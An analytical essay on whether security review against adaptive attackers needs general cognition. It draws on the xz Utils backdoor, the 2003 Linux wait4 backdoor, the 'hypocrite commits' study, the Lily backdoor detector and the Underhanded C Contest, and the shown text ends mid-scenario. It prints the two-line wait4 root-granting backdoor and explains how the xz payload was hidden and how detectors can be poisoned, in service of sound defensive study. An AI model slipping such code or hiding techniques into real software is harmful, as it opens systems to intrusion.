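# Does security review against capable adversaries require general cognition?

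## The argument that defence must be as broad as offence

Security review means examining something an outsider submits, such as a change to a program, an email or a post on a website, and deciding whether to let it through. People once did nearly all of this work, but programs now do much of it, and how much such a program needs to be able to do is an open question. A program built only for review might come to do the job better than any human. But some submissions come from skilled people who want the review to fail, so doing the job well might require the general understanding that people bring to it.

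Code review is the clearest example of the problem. In many software projects, a contributor proposes a change and a reviewer reads it before it enters the program. The reviewer has little time and works from the changed lines, the contributor's explanation and, usually, some automated tests.

Even honest contributors can submit changes that are wrong. *Can chatbots craft correct code?* (2025), from the security company Trail of Bits, describes a fix that Claude, Anthropic's language model, proposed for a crash in a program called Vendetect. An engineer at the company reviewed it. Claude's explanation seemed plausible and the fix stopped the crash, but Vendetect's output was now empty and its unit tests (automatic checks on individual parts of a program) failed. The problem was in a function that calls itself. Long chains of such calls can overflow the memory Python sets aside for them, but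 the engineer knew that this function's inputs never took it more than a few calls deep, which Claude had apparently not taken into account.

The mistake was easy to expose because nobody had tried to hide it. A dishonest contributor could prepare whatever evidence the reviewer relies on. They would run the tests first, submit the change only once the tests passed, and work on making the explanation plausible. They might even spend years on useful work to earn trust, as did the person who planted a backdoor (a hidden function that gives access to whoever knows how to trigger it) in the xz compression library.

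A change of this kind is an adversarial input, one that someone has chosen or built to make a system give the wrong answer. An adaptive adversary is an attacker who studies the defence and changes method in response.

### Average case and worst case

A dishonest contributor changes what counts as a good reviewer. Let ℓ(x) be 1 if the reviewer decides wrongly about a change x, and 0 if the reviewer decides rightly. Honest changes come from a distribution D that reflects the mistakes people ordinarily make, and the relevant measure is the average error, E[ℓ(x)] for x drawn from D. An attacker instead chooses x from the set X of all the changes he could submit, so the relevant measure becomes the maximum of ℓ(x) over X. If even one harmful change in X would get past the reviewer, that maximum is 1, however small the average error is.

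A reviewer that rarely misses honest mistakes can still be easy for an attacker to get past, as some made-up numbers show. Suppose an automated reviewer passes one harmful change in ten thousand. If honest contributors submit a hundred harmful mistakes a year, the project will accept one per century, on average. But an attacker with a private copy of the reviewer can test variants of his attack until one passes, and submit only that one. If every variant has the same independent chance ε = 1/10,000 of passing, he needs 1/ε, or ten thousand, attempts on average, which a computer can make for him. If the reviewer passed a tenth as many harmful changes, he would need ten times as many attempts. This calculation overstates the danger from an attacker who has no copy to practise on and is banned after his first failure, since he has little chance of succeeding. It also assumes that the attacker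 searches blindly, when a real one would learn from each refusal and could need fewer attempts.

A reader's comment on the essay *worst case thinking in ai alignment* illustrates the same difference with programs that sort lists. The easiest input for nearly all of them is a list already in order, while the hardest depends much more on the sorting method. Similarly, the inputs that defeat a reviewer are particular to that reviewer, so an attacker benefits from studying it. The reviewer's record on ordinary inputs may not reveal these weaknesses, as with the superhuman Go programs that lose to weak opponents. The comment also mentions an intermediate measure that engineers use for response times, such as how well a system does on all but the slowest one per cent of requests. A website can reasonably promise this, but a security reviewer faces attackers who will aim for the excluded one per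 cent.

### Five premises

If worst-case performance is what matters in security review, a reviewer may seem to need cognition as broad as its attackers'.

1. The service succeeds or fails on inputs that someone chose in order to defeat it.
2. A capable adversary can use any strategy and any knowledge.
3. To catch an attack, the reviewer must represent the strategy or the goal behind it.
4. So a superhuman reviewer must cover the whole range of offence.
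5. That range is as wide as general cognition, meaning the ability to learn, reason and plan across many unrelated domains, including about the goals of other agents.

It would follow that a superhuman reviewer has general cognition. (It would not follow that it has goals of its own; the definition leaves that out on purpose.)

This five-step form is a reconstruction rather than any one author's wording. A similar argument appears in Scott Alexander's *Book Review: Reframing Superintelligence* (2019), an essay on a report by Eric Drexler, then a researcher at Oxford's Future of Humanity Institute. Alexander objects that many tasks require general intelligence, and gives the example of planning a defence against nuclear attack, for which there are too few past cases to train a program. People who take on such a task use something like common sense, which he presumes they have because they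 understand thousands of domains "from gardening to ballistics". Alexander argues from the lack of examples, while the five premises start from the attacker's freedom. In practice the two arguments are similar, because attackers benefit from looking for attacks that have no past examples.

The premises are not equally strong. Premise 1 omits the requirement that the service also do well on honest changes, which are the majority. A reviewer that refuses every change has perfect worst-case security but is useless, and a defence that treats every odd-looking change as hostile will fail on the honest ones.

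Premise 2 is close to true of how an attacker can prepare. He can read anything, flatter anyone and invent colleagues who vouch for him. But the reviewer receives only certain lines in certain files, with a message attached.

That matters for premise 3, on which most of the argument depends. Many attack strategies lead to the same harmful effect. Whether the attacker bribed the maintainer or impersonated him, the changed program must do something it should not, such as send out a password or run a stranger's commands. A checker that recognises every harmful effect a change to this program could have does not need to represent the attacker's possible strategies, and there may be far fewer effects than strategies. In the same way, the Vendetect tests showed that the output was wrong without explaining how Claude had come to propose it.

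A good reply is that whether an effect is harmful often depends on what the program is for. Opening a network connection is normal for a web browser but would be alarming in a program that resizes photographs. To list E, somebody has to state what the program may do, and for a large program that statement may be long and disputed, or nobody may have written it. Without such a statement, a reviewer has to judge what a change is for, which is where premise 3 began.

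Premise 4 relies on two meanings of "superhuman". A reviewer that catches twice as many attacks as the best human reviewers is superhuman in the usual sense, but it may still miss many. The step to "the whole range of offence" is valid only if "superhuman" means missing nothing, or nothing that any capable attacker could find. Human reviewers have general cognition, and they don't meet that standard either.

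Premise 5 concerns the breadth of offence. An attack on code might draw on the quirks of a compiler, the habits of a tired maintainer and the date of a public holiday, and it is hard to name a field of knowledge that could never help an attacker. But only some of what attackers might draw on works against a particular system, and its defender only has to worry about that part.

### An ancestor in biology

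The idea behind premise 5, that opponents require general intelligence in a way that mere problems do not, has a well-known precedent in the study of animal minds. Humphrey (1976), in *The social function of intellect*, asked why apes show impressive creative reasoning in the laboratory yet seem to have little use for it in the wild. Humphrey had spent two months watching gorillas in the Virunga mountains, and they did little but eat, sleep and play. Chimpanzees do fish for termites with probes, but they learn the technique by trial and error or by copying others. He guessed that higher primates can solve most of their practical problems with techniques learned in these ways.

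A social animal that wants to change another's behaviour faces a partner that reacts and may change its tactics in turn. Humphrey compared this to chess, where accumulated knowledge alone is not enough and the player has to look ahead along a branching tree of moves and replies. He illustrated the idea with Robinson Crusoe, whose real difficulties began when Man Friday arrived. Since an animal's rivals belong to its own breeding community, any heritable trait that helps it outwit them will spread and raise the standard for everyone, an effect Humphrey called a ratchet. Byrne and Whiten elaborated the idea in 1988 under the name Machiavellian intelligence.

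Even if Humphrey was right about the pressure, the abilities it produces need not be general. *Group Size Predicts Social but Not Nonsocial Cognition in Lemurs* (MacLean, Sandel and colleagues, 2013) compared six lemur species with different group sizes. In the social task, sixty animals could take food from one of two human competitors, only one of whom could see it. Species from larger groups were better at choosing the food that the competitor could not see. Group size did not predict performance on the nonsocial task, which measured how well an animal holds back an impulsive response. This fits the view that living among rivals improves the skills for dealing with them and leaves other skills roughly unchanged.

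If the same held for machines, an adversary would force a defender to become good only at dealing with adversaries, which is much less than premise 5 needs. But six species and a single nonsocial task are limited evidence. When the researchers left out the ring-tailed lemurs, which live in the largest groups and scored best, the link held only in the condition where one competitor had turned her back. Dunbar and Shultz (2017), in *Why are there so many explanations for primate brain evolution?*, leave open the other possibility, that one domain-general form of cognition may have supported both social and foraging skills.

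A difference between animals and machines also weakens the comparison, whatever the biology shows. Evolution had to fit all of an animal's abilities into one body and one brain. In Alexander's account of Drexler's view, people who want to run fast, lift weights and fight off enemies have built the car, the crane and the gun as separate machines.

### Comprehensive AI Services

In *Reframing Superintelligence*, Drexler (2019) built a general picture of advanced AI on that difference, which he called Comprehensive AI Services. The five premises matter mainly because of their implications for this picture. In it, superhuman ability comes from a large and growing collection of services that each perform a task, such as translating, designing engines or helping to develop new services. Together they could come to cover whatever people can do, without any single system having to do everything or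 pursue open-ended goals in the world.

Part of Drexler's case is that optimising a system hard for one task narrows it. A racing car cannot carry a busload of passengers, and an efficient translation program will never plan a route for a vehicle. Capabilities that do not serve the task still take up memory, training time and computation, so a development process that penalises the use of these resources will remove such capabilities, and the harder it optimises, the fewer will remain. In systems optimised in this way, Drexler writes, components "will have no spare time to daydream about world domination". This holds only if the objective is bounded in space, time and scope, and the measure of success penalises both resource use and side effects. He thinks services meet these conditions naturally.

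He adds that even when nobody understands a system's inner workings, we can know a good deal about what it can do by knowing what went into it. Information absent from its inputs, in training and in use, will be absent from its outputs. The system may infer some things it was not given, but nobody could infer a Wikipedia article from a knowledge of physics that contained no language. He calls the limits of a system's competence "fuzzy, yet bounded", and abilities far from its task, such as theorem-proving in a vision system, will reliably be missing. Developers can tighten these limits by giving the system efficient external tools. The pressure to economise will keep it from developing the same abilities internally, and its use of the tools will be visible.

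All of this depends on identifying what is off-task, which an adversary makes difficult. Vehicle routes will always be off-task for a translator, but a calendar of public holidays becomes relevant to a code reviewer once an attacker times a change to arrive when the maintainers are away. If premises 2 and 3 hold, a cost-conscious developer could not safely strip anything out of a review service, and optimising it harder would make it broader.

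Drexler also could not easily treat security as an exception, because the services that would have to be general are the ones that protect all the rest. He writes that effective countermeasures against bad actors may need strongly optimised AI, and Alexander reads him as hoping that superhuman services, including anomaly detectors for rogue systems, will help to contain dangerous agents when somebody builds one.

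The five premises could all be true without refuting Drexler's main claim, that general ability does not require a general agent. Drexler argues at length in his report that a system can have a bounded task and unbounded knowledge of the world. His example is translation, which benefits from knowledge of everything that people write about. According to Alexander, Drexler also accepts that some services will need fairly complete models of the world, reasoning across many domains and the ability to learn on the fly, but denies that they must therefore be agents. If true, the premises would still undercut the more reassuring claim that hard optimisation keeps each service narrow.

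In *Comments on Comprehensive AI Services*, Ngo (2019) was sceptical of many of Drexler's conclusions. He argued that powerful services are hard to make safe individually, while weak ones are hard to combine into a system that can compete with a single unified agent. He also argued that many complex tasks do not split into parts with clean boundaries. Where several services need similar mental abilities, he thought it would probably be more efficient to merge them into one system, and more efficient still if that system could learn new tasks quickly without retraining, as people do.

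Security work seems well suited to such a merger, because code reviewers, spam filters and moderators of online posts all benefit from a good guess at what a hostile person is trying to do. But Ngo's point is about efficiency, so it gives a reason to expect that people will build general reviewers, not to think that narrow ones must fail.

Ngo was also sympathetic to the idea that services would replace people in most cognitively difficult jobs before any general system arrived. He imagined a program that learns from court documents to imitate lawyers well enough to replace them in most cases, without understanding law as people do. But success in most cases describes average performance, and an opposing lawyer who knew how the program worked would exploit its worst-case performance by bringing it the cases it handles badly.

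After large language models arrived, Drexler revisited his report. He wrote that he had envisioned specialised systems for specialised services, but the new models showed that a single general technology could provide many distinct services, including translation, summaries, medical answers and code. He did not take this as a defeat, since developers still adapt such models to particular jobs with further training and instructions, and on his account generality makes specialising easier. But a reviewer made from a language model starts with broad abilities whether or not reviewing requires them, so the success of such reviewers cannot by itself show whether the breadth was necessary.

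### Three distinctions

"General" can refer to at least three things, and a system may have some without the others. Broad knowledge is a stock of facts from many fields, such as which functions of a programming language are risky or how a forged email tends to read. General reasoning is the ability to combine such facts in ways the system has not been shown before. Having goals means trying to bring about some state of the world and choosing actions accordingly. A large list of known attacks has broad knowledge but neither of the others. Drexler argues that human-like competence does not bring human-like goals with it, though he grants that skill at acting flexibly in the human world carries special risks. Alexander is less sure that the three can be separated so cleanly. Natural minds choose what to attend to and which question to take up next, and he asks whether systems that do the same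 will eventually outperform those that do not. A code reviewer makes this kind of choice when it decides which of a thousand files to open.

A task may also *require* general cognition or merely *favour* it. It requires general cognition if no narrow system could do it to the required standard. It favours general cognition if general systems are cheaper to build for it, or if training on it tends to produce them. Ngo's argument for merging services and Humphrey's ratchet show at most that a task favours general cognition. Evidence for a requirement has to come from narrow systems that fail because they lack breadth, and a single narrow system that succeeds would refute the requirement. Even limited comparisons are of some use. *Mythos and Cybersecurity* (2026), an essay on Bruce Schneier's website, reports that Anthropic withheld its model Mythos Preview from general release because of its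 skill at finding software flaws, and that the security company Aisle reproduced many of the published examples with smaller, cheaper public models. So those findings did not require the largest model, although repeating a discovery is easier than making it. It is harder to tell whether they required general ability.

An attacker model is a representation of what an attacker wants, knows and can do, used to predict or recognise attacks. A service can build one at run time, while it reviews a submission. For example, if a contributor is pressing for a quick release and his explanation does not match the code, the service can consider what he would gain. Alternatively, the service's designers can build the model beforehand and include only the result in the service. A rule that two people must approve any change to the login code comes from someone thinking about a bribed or impersonated maintainer,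 but the program that enforces it only has to count approvals. Similarly, Humphrey's chimpanzees can use termite probes without having to invent the technique.

If the designers can do the work in advance, premise 3 may be true of the defence as a whole and false of the service. But a fixed rule doesn't change while an adaptive adversary studies it, and once he finds a way round it, somebody has to revise it. People can do that if attacks change every few years, and the service can stay simple. If attacks change by the hour, either the service has to do the thinking or another automated system has to rewrite the service's rules, in which case the general cognition will be in that system.

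## Three attempts to plant backdoors in open-source software

According to Premise 3, a reviewer must represent the strategy or goal behind an attack to catch it. Open-source software is a good test of this claim because anyone can propose changes and much of the discussion is public. Three attempts to get harmful code into such software, one of them an experiment by university researchers, are documented well enough to show what exposed each one.

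### xz Utils

xz Utils is a collection of compression tools whose library, liblzma, comes with most Linux systems. For years a volunteer called Lasse Collin maintained it almost alone. Late in 2021 a contributor using the name Jia Tan began to send patches, and they were useful. In 2022 several people with little or no other history online complained on the project's mailing list that Collin was too slow, and urged him to bring in another maintainer. Tan took on more and more of the work, and by 2023 could approve changes and publish releases. In February 2024, a little over two years after the first patches, Tan published a release with a backdoor in it.

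The backdoor had two parts. The larger part was in the public repository, inside two compressed files that looked like test data. A compression library needs such files, including deliberately damaged ones, and nobody can read them by eye. The other part, a line in a build script that activated the first, was only in the release archives, the packaged source code that many Linux distributions download and build. Someone reviewing the repository would have found only some odd data that nothing used.

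When a distribution built the package, the extra line unpacked a hidden script from one of the test files. If the machine was a common type of Linux computer and the build was for a Debian or RPM package (the two main formats), the script altered the build to put the payload in liblzma. People use ssh to log in to remote machines, and on Debian and several other systems, the ssh server loads liblzma indirectly. Once loaded, the payload replaced a function that the server calls when it checks a user's key.

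Andres Freund, a database developer who said he was not a security researcher, found the xz backdoor by investigating slow ssh logins. In *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, Freund (2024) described noticing over some weeks that ssh logins on Debian systems were using a lot of processor time, and that valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory, was reporting errors. In the copy of his message that Patrakov (2024) reposted the next day, a refused login takes 0.299 seconds before the new library is installed and 0.807 seconds after. Freund recorded the path the processor took through the code with the backdoor active and inactive, and looked for where the two recordings diverged. The slow step was the payload's search through tables in memory for the functions it needed.

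Freund could notice and trace the delay without a theory about an attacker, but he needed one to decide whom to tell. The person who had committed the test files had also discussed "fixes" for the valgrind errors on several mailing lists, so Freund thought it more likely that this person was involved than that someone had broken into their computer. He therefore reported the problem to Debian's security team and then to a mailing list for Linux distributions, rather than to the xz project.

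A simple program could not easily have replaced Freund, though. An automatic test that timed logins before and after each update would have flagged a half-second delay, but somebody would have had to think of timing ssh logins to test a compression library. The backdoor also stayed inactive under many of the conditions in which developers run tests, and Freund saw no slowdown when he first started the server by hand. Finding it took curiosity and a broad knowledge of how the parts of a Linux system fit together, though no knowledge of attackers. The delay was also a mistake by the attacker, and if the backdoor's search had been faster, Freund might have noticed nothing except the memory errors, which Tan was already working to remove.

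Detecting the social part of the attack earlier would have been even harder. New contributors who send useful patches, impatient users and tired maintainers who accept help are all common, and nearly all of them are genuine. An observer would have had to notice that the complaining accounts had no history and all pushed for the same outcome, and then ask who stood to gain, to suspect Tan in 2022. This is the kind of modelling that premise 3 describes.

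*Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) discusses a machine-learning tool by Ganz and colleagues that searches a project's history for unusual behaviour by contributors. It caught 15 of 19 attacks, but its average false alarm rate was 10.75%, which is far too high for accusing volunteers of sabotage. Somebody also has to act on an alarm. In *open source and code review*, a reader's comment on the Linux news site LWN, pizza (2024) says the trouble with xz was that its only active maintainer was the attacker, and nobody else was willing or able to review that maintainer's work.

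A much narrower check might have worked without anyone having to judge Tan. It would compare each release archive with the repository and flag every line that appears only in the archive. It would also flag harmless differences, because archives often contain automatically generated files that the repository lacks, and the attacker hid the extra line where people expect such differences. A project would have to explain these differences or stop producing them, but it could do so without guessing what an attacker wants.

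### The Linux kernel in 2003

Twenty years earlier, the same kind of comparison had exposed an attack on the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system. The kernel's developers kept the master copy of their code in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked BitKeeper, so there was also a mirror in another system, CVS. According to a 2013 account on the blog Freedom to Tinker, every change in the master copy carried a pointer to the record of its approval. On 5 November 2003 Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the mirror that had no such pointer and was missing from the master copy. Someone had apparently broken into the mirror's server and inserted it.

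The change added two lines to wait4, a function that a program calls when it wants to wait for something to happen:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

This code gives root access, which allows a user to do anything, to any program that calls wait4 with a particular combination of options. It looks like a check that forbids that combination and returns an error. But the first line uses a single equals sign, which assigns a value in C, instead of the double one that compares values. It therefore sets the current user's number to 0, which is root's number, instead of testing whether it is already 0. The assignment itself has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the second line never runs and the program gets no error message.

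On the kernel's mailing list, Zwane Mwaikambo said the line looked odd, and Chad Kitching wrote that it looked like an attempt to backdoor the kernel. McVoy (2003) replied that it certainly did, and that he had missed it.

McVoy discovered the change through its provenance, the record of where a piece of code came from and who approved it. A short program can check that every change has an approval record and that a mirror matches its original without analyzing the C code, and it will flag a harmless stray line as readily as a backdoor. Dilger (2003), in another reply, credited the catch to the "paranoia" that had led McVoy to add extra checks when exporting the data, and thought that a change like this might otherwise have taken a good while to find. McVoy had thought beforehand about how a copy might come to differ from its original, so the checks could detect the difference without further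 reasoning.

Mwaikambo and Kitching had to read the code, but they may not have needed a model of the attacker to see that something was wrong. Kitching pointed out that the line set the user number, and that the error code it seemed to produce was useless because the next line of the function overwrote it. A reviewer looking only for mistakes could have questioned either point. Writing one equals sign instead of two is a common mistake in C. Compilers can warn about it, but by convention an extra pair of brackets, which this line had, marks the assignment as intended and suppresses the warning. It would have been harder to get around a rule that only a few named functions, which do not include wait4, may change a user number. Kitching's guess about intent mattered more for deciding what to do next, because a mistake only needs correcting, while a backdoor means that somebody should examine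 the server.

The provenance check worked because the attacker had bypassed the approval process. It would not have caught the xz backdoor, because Tan had become part of that process and the test files were properly approved. Dilger also wondered about adding digital signatures, which would prove that a change came from the developer it named. Signatures would not have exposed the xz backdoor either, since the files did come from Jia Tan.

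### Hypocrite commits

The third attempt went through ordinary review, and the people behind it had no standing in the project. In *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, Wu and Lu of the University of Minnesota claimed that an outsider could plant vulnerabilities in the Linux kernel through small patches that seem to fix something, which they called hypocrite commits. A vulnerability usually needs several conditions at once. A use-after-free, for example, requires that a program release a piece of memory, that it use that memory, and that the use come after the release, when the memory may already hold something else. Wu and Lu therefore looked for places where some of the conditions already held and a patch of a few lines could supply the rest.

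Honest contributors had already done the same thing by accident. One real patch added a line that released a device after its registration had failed, which looked like ordinary cleanup. But the line could also free memory that another function was about to use and free again, and the flaw stayed in the kernel for five years. Wu and Lu collected 138 recorded vulnerabilities that small patches had introduced. They also counted more than 6,000 places in the kernel where one of the conditions for a use-after-free was still missing. They estimated that maintainers catch about 19% of newly introduced use-after-free flaws in concurrent code (code in which several things run at the same time).

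In August 2020 the researchers tried their method on the kernel's maintainers, using false names. *A Full Disclosure of the Case Study of the “Hypocrite Commits” Paper* (2021) gives their account of the four patches in the study. They had believed all four were flawed, but one turned out to be correct, and the maintainers merged it. Maintainers dropped the second because it was almost the same as a patch someone else had submitted in 2019, which the project had accepted and then had to remove because it caused a use-after-free. The maintainer who reviewed the third found a coding problem and a separate bug but missed the use-after-free that the researchers had planted. The maintainer who reviewed the fourth also objected to something else and missed the planted flaw.

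The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, a group of kernel developers, later reviewed the university's submissions and found that none of the buggy code had reached the main version of the kernel, according to TechRadar's *Linux review board says rogue researchers did not successfully insert buggy patches*. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) confirmed this and added that review had stopped all four patches. That does not fit the researchers' account of the correct patch.

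However, maintainers recognised the planted flaw in only one of the three patches, and they did so because they remembered an earlier mistake. They objected to the other two for different reasons, so a real attacker would have fixed what the maintainer objected to and resubmitted the patch with the planted flaw still in it. Three patches are too few to estimate a detection rate, and the researchers' accounts of them differ. Wu and Lu (2020) wrote in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)* that once a maintainer replied that a patch looked good, they immediately pointed out the flaw and asked him not to apply it, and that the maintainers agreed in all three cases. According to the disclosure four months later, the maintainers' own objections stopped the flawed patches.

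A few days after the last of these patches, Wu asked how the project dealt with the risk of malicious contributors. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior kernel developer, replied that all contributors make mistakes, so everyone's patches need the same checking. This was his reason for not looking for bad faith. He put the number of new contributors at about 1,000 a year. At that rate, a monitor that wrongly flagged one newcomer in a hundred as malicious would flag about ten honest people a year.

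He also explained that kernel developers trust people to be around to fix their own mistakes, not to get everything right, and that they don't review again what a trusted colleague has reviewed. Jia Tan would have met this standard, because Tan was there to deal with the memory errors that the backdoor in xz caused.

Kroah-Hartman tried to judge intent the following spring and apparently got it wrong. On 6 April 2021, another researcher at the university posted a poor patch. According to LWN, one developer questioned it the next day and a second rejected it the day after. On 20 April, Kroah-Hartman accused the sender of submitting patches known to be invalid and began removing the university's earlier contributions. In its statement, the university maintains that the April patches were poor but sent in good faith. Machek (2021), a kernel developer who replied to the board's report, also saw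 no deception that year. Kroah-Hartman's suspicion was understandable, since people at the same university had deceived the maintainers eight months before, but reviewers had already rejected the patch without judging its author. His suspicion led to a re-review involving 85 developers, according to a reader's count in the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021).

Wu and Lu withdrew their paper on 26 April 2021, after a leading security conference had accepted it. In their letter to the conference, they wrote that they had experimented on the kernel community without its consent (Wu and Lu, 2021). They did not want to benefit from an improperly conducted study or to have others take it as a model. These objections concern how they ran the study and don't address whether its claim was true.

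### An automatic check for backdoors

Maintainers missed two of the three planted flaws, and the xz backdoor was discovered largely by chance, so a quick automatic check would be valuable. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli built such a check, called Lily. It extends fuzzing, which runs a program on many automatically generated inputs to find misbehaviour. Some large projects already fuzz each change for about ten minutes to look for crashes. A backdoor normally causes no crash, because the program is doing what the attacker intended. Lily therefore monitors system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, connect to a network or start another program. A program can affect the outside world only through these calls, so a useful backdoor has to make them.

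For an input x, let N(x) be the set of types of system call that the new version of the program makes, and O(x) the set that the old version makes. Before the fuzzing starts, Lily runs the new version on inputs saved from earlier rounds and collects all the sets that occur. Call this collection T. Lily then raises an alarm about an input x if

N(x) ∉ T and N(x) ≠ O(x).

The first condition means that the behaviour is untypical of the new version, and the second means that the change introduced it. If an honest update makes a server log every request, N(x) will differ from O(x) for every input, but the sets in T will also include the logging, so there is no alarm. An old, rarely used feature may be missing from T, but the old version behaves the same way, so again there is no alarm. A new backdoor usually meets both conditions.

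In 2011 attackers replaced the official release of vsFTPd, a program for transferring files, with one that opened a root shell (a command line with unlimited powers) to anyone who gave a username containing ":)". When Kokkonis and colleagues fuzzed this release, the fuzzer eventually generated such a username and saved it because it reached code that no earlier input had reached. The system calls that followed had never occurred together in the saved inputs, and the previous release did not produce them either. Lily then traced them to seven lines in one file, out of 1,407 lines in five files that differed between the two releases. In those seven lines, a reader can see the program open a network connection and start a shell.

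The researchers tested Lily on 13 backdoors, three from real attacks and ten written for a benchmark. They put each one into a single change and into several full releases, and ran Lily 20 times on each. Lily blocked the backdoored changes in 233 of 260 runs (90%) and the backdoored releases in 828 of 1,000 (83%). It caught every one of them at least once in 20 runs, but a project that vets each change only once could miss a backdoor. Lily blocked the backdoored change to one sound library in only 13 of 20 runs.

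Lily raised false alarms in only 0.2% of runs on harmless changes and 4.3% of runs on harmless releases. Almost all the false alarms on releases came from two releases of the same sound library, both of which Lily blocked every time. Requiring behaviour to be both untypical and new kept the rates much lower than either test alone. With only the test for untypical behaviour, the rates were 14% for changes and 20% for releases, and with only the test for new behaviour they were 10% and 58%.

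These are average results on backdoors that nobody had designed to evade Lily. The tool is public, so an attacker could test versions of a backdoor against it until one went undetected. The researchers examined several ways of doing this, including putting the backdoor in code the fuzzer rarely reaches. Across 337 code changes in 12 projects, fuzzing covered only about 32% on average, mainly because the harnesses, the small programs that feed inputs to a project, were old or incomplete. With modern harnesses, coverage was usually nearly complete.

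An attacker could also poison Lily's record of normal behaviour by first adding the trigger without the harmful code. Lily would then save inputs that set off the trigger, and later treat the backdoor's behaviour as typical. With 100 such inputs saved, detection fell to 54% on changes and 46% on releases. A stricter mode restored detection but raised false alarms to about 3% and 18%, respectively.

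A backdoor with a cryptographic trigger is harder for Lily to detect, because random inputs have practically no chance of setting it off. The xz backdoor had such a trigger, and xz was not among the 13 test cases. Its payload also stayed inactive unless it was running inside the ssh server, so fuzzing the compression library alone would not have activated it. Freund followed up a delay, but Lily records which calls a program makes, not how long it takes. Kokkonis and colleagues do point out that code which fuzzing never reaches stands out in coverage reports, and suggest that this may be why the xz attackers turned off the project's automatic fuzzing.

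The other two attempts would probably have escaped detection too. The 2003 change altered a number inside the kernel, which requires no further system call. A hypocrite commit contains only a memory flaw that someone can exploit later, with no hidden function for Lily to observe. Ordinary fuzzing might find such a flaw if it caused a crash.

When Lily catches a backdoor, it does so by comparing sets, without modeling what an attacker wants. Its designers did think about attackers when they decided that a backdoor must make system calls, and again when they worked out how someone might poison the saved inputs and built the stricter mode in response. Premise 3 is therefore false of Lily at run time, at least on this benchmark, but closer to true of the researchers who will have to revise Lily if attackers adapt.

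### Backdoors that nobody caught

Nobody found any of these attacks by first working out what an attacker was planning. But the record includes only backdoors that somebody caught, and these may differ from the rest. Suppose attackers make 100 attempts, 50 of them careless and 50 careful. If defenders catch 80% of the careless ones, through slow logins or missing records, and 2% of the careful ones, they will know of 41 attempts, 40 of them careless. It will seem that defenders hardly ever need to understand attackers, while 49 careful backdoors remain in use. The record is most likely to omit the attacks that defenders could find only with a good model of the attacker.

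The number of undetected backdoors could also be close to zero, and the record is not enough to tell. Kokkonis and colleagues note that documented incidents are rare. An LWN reader remarked that if the hypocrite commits had come from someone who never published a paper about them, probably nobody would have spotted them.

Even when a maintainer finds and fixes a planted flaw, it may be recorded as an ordinary bug. The use-after-free that stayed in the kernel for five years is considered an honest mistake, and there is no reason to doubt that, but a careful attacker would try to leave a flaw that looked just the same.

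Experiments avoid part of this problem, because the people who plant the flaws know how many there are. Wu and Lu could report that maintainers missed two of three planted flaws, but nobody can calculate that rate for real attacks. The rate still depends on how well the experimenters hide the flaws. A researcher with a few weeks and a patch of under five lines may not be representative of an attacker willing to spend two years on useful work first.

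## The Underhanded C Contest and what human reviewers miss

Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University, ran eight rounds of the Underhanded C Contest, from 2005 to 2009 and from 2013 to 2015. In each round, he challenged programmers to write a short C program that did an ordinary job but also had a hidden malicious effect, both of which he specified. The best entries looked innocent to other programmers, and anyone who found the bug could still take it for an honest mistake.

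In the contest's *FAQ*, Craver traces the idea to Daniel Horn's Obfuscated V contest of 2004, whose entrants wrote programs that miscounted votes. Some programs failed only on election day, so testing on any other day would not reveal the fault. Craver wanted to learn what underhanded tactics could do and what made them possible.

Underhanded code differs from obfuscated code, which its author deliberately makes hard to read. In the rules that accompany *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (2016), Craver says his contest is in many ways "the exact opposite" of the obfuscated C competition. Wheeler's study for the Institute for Defense Analyses, *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (2020), excludes obfuscated code because reviewers can distrust it simply for being hard to understand, without working out what it hides. The xz attacker avoided this kind of distrust by using test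 files, which have a good reason to be unreadable.

### Recovering pixels from a black rectangle

In *2008 Underhanded C Contest Officially Open*, Craver asked for a program that blacks out part of an image but lets someone recover the missing pixels. In *2008 Winners*, Craver (2009) reported more than 100 entries, and many used one of two methods. Some scrambled the pixels with a pseudo-random mask that the attacker could regenerate. Others left a copy of the data at the end of the file, where image viewers ignore it. Both can look odd, since scrambling is a strange way to blank out a pixel and someone may notice the extra data.

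John Meacham's winning program, 55 lines long, did neither. It works on a version of the PPM image format that stores a picture as text, with three numbers per pixel for red, green and blue. It reads the file one character at a time and replaces every digit inside the rectangle with a 0. A bright pixel written as "255 240 96" becomes "000 000 00", and a dark one written as "12 7 0" becomes "00 0 0". An image viewer reads all of these as zero and shows solid black. But anyone who opens the file as text can count the digits and tell whether each number was below 10, from 10 to 99, or higher, which is easily enough to read black writing on a white page.

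The C is simple, but to see the fault, a reader has to know that the format allows extra zeros and notice that the program replaces digits rather than whole numbers. The reader also has to know what the black rectangle is for, because the same code would be correct in a program that draws black boxes as decoration. Guessing Meacham's goal would have helped a great deal. Someone who suspects that an attacker wants to recover the pixels will ask what in the output still depends on them, and the uneven rows of zeros are the obvious place to look.

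A tester could ask the same question without suspecting anybody. The tester would run the program on pairs of images that differ only in the random contents of the rectangle, and check that each pair produces identical output files. This would expose Meacham's entry as well as the masks and the appended copies. But somebody would first have to specify that the output must not depend on the hidden pixels. If the specification said only that the rectangle should come out black, Meacham's program would pass.

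Meacham could also have given a sensible technical answer if a maintainer had asked why he wrote the code this way. In a comment under the results, he pointed out that working character by character avoided a problem with fgets, a standard C function for reading text, and that a version without the leak would have been more complicated or buggy.

### Passing off a fake warhead

For the 2015 round, Craver worked with the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works to reduce the danger from nuclear and other weapons. In the scenario, two countries have agreed to destroy warheads. Inspectors need to confirm that each warhead is real, but seeing its gamma-ray spectrum (the number of rays detected at each energy) would reveal secrets about its design. A program therefore compares the spectrum with a reference and outputs only yes or no. Entrants had to write the program so that it would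 secretly output yes for a fake warhead.

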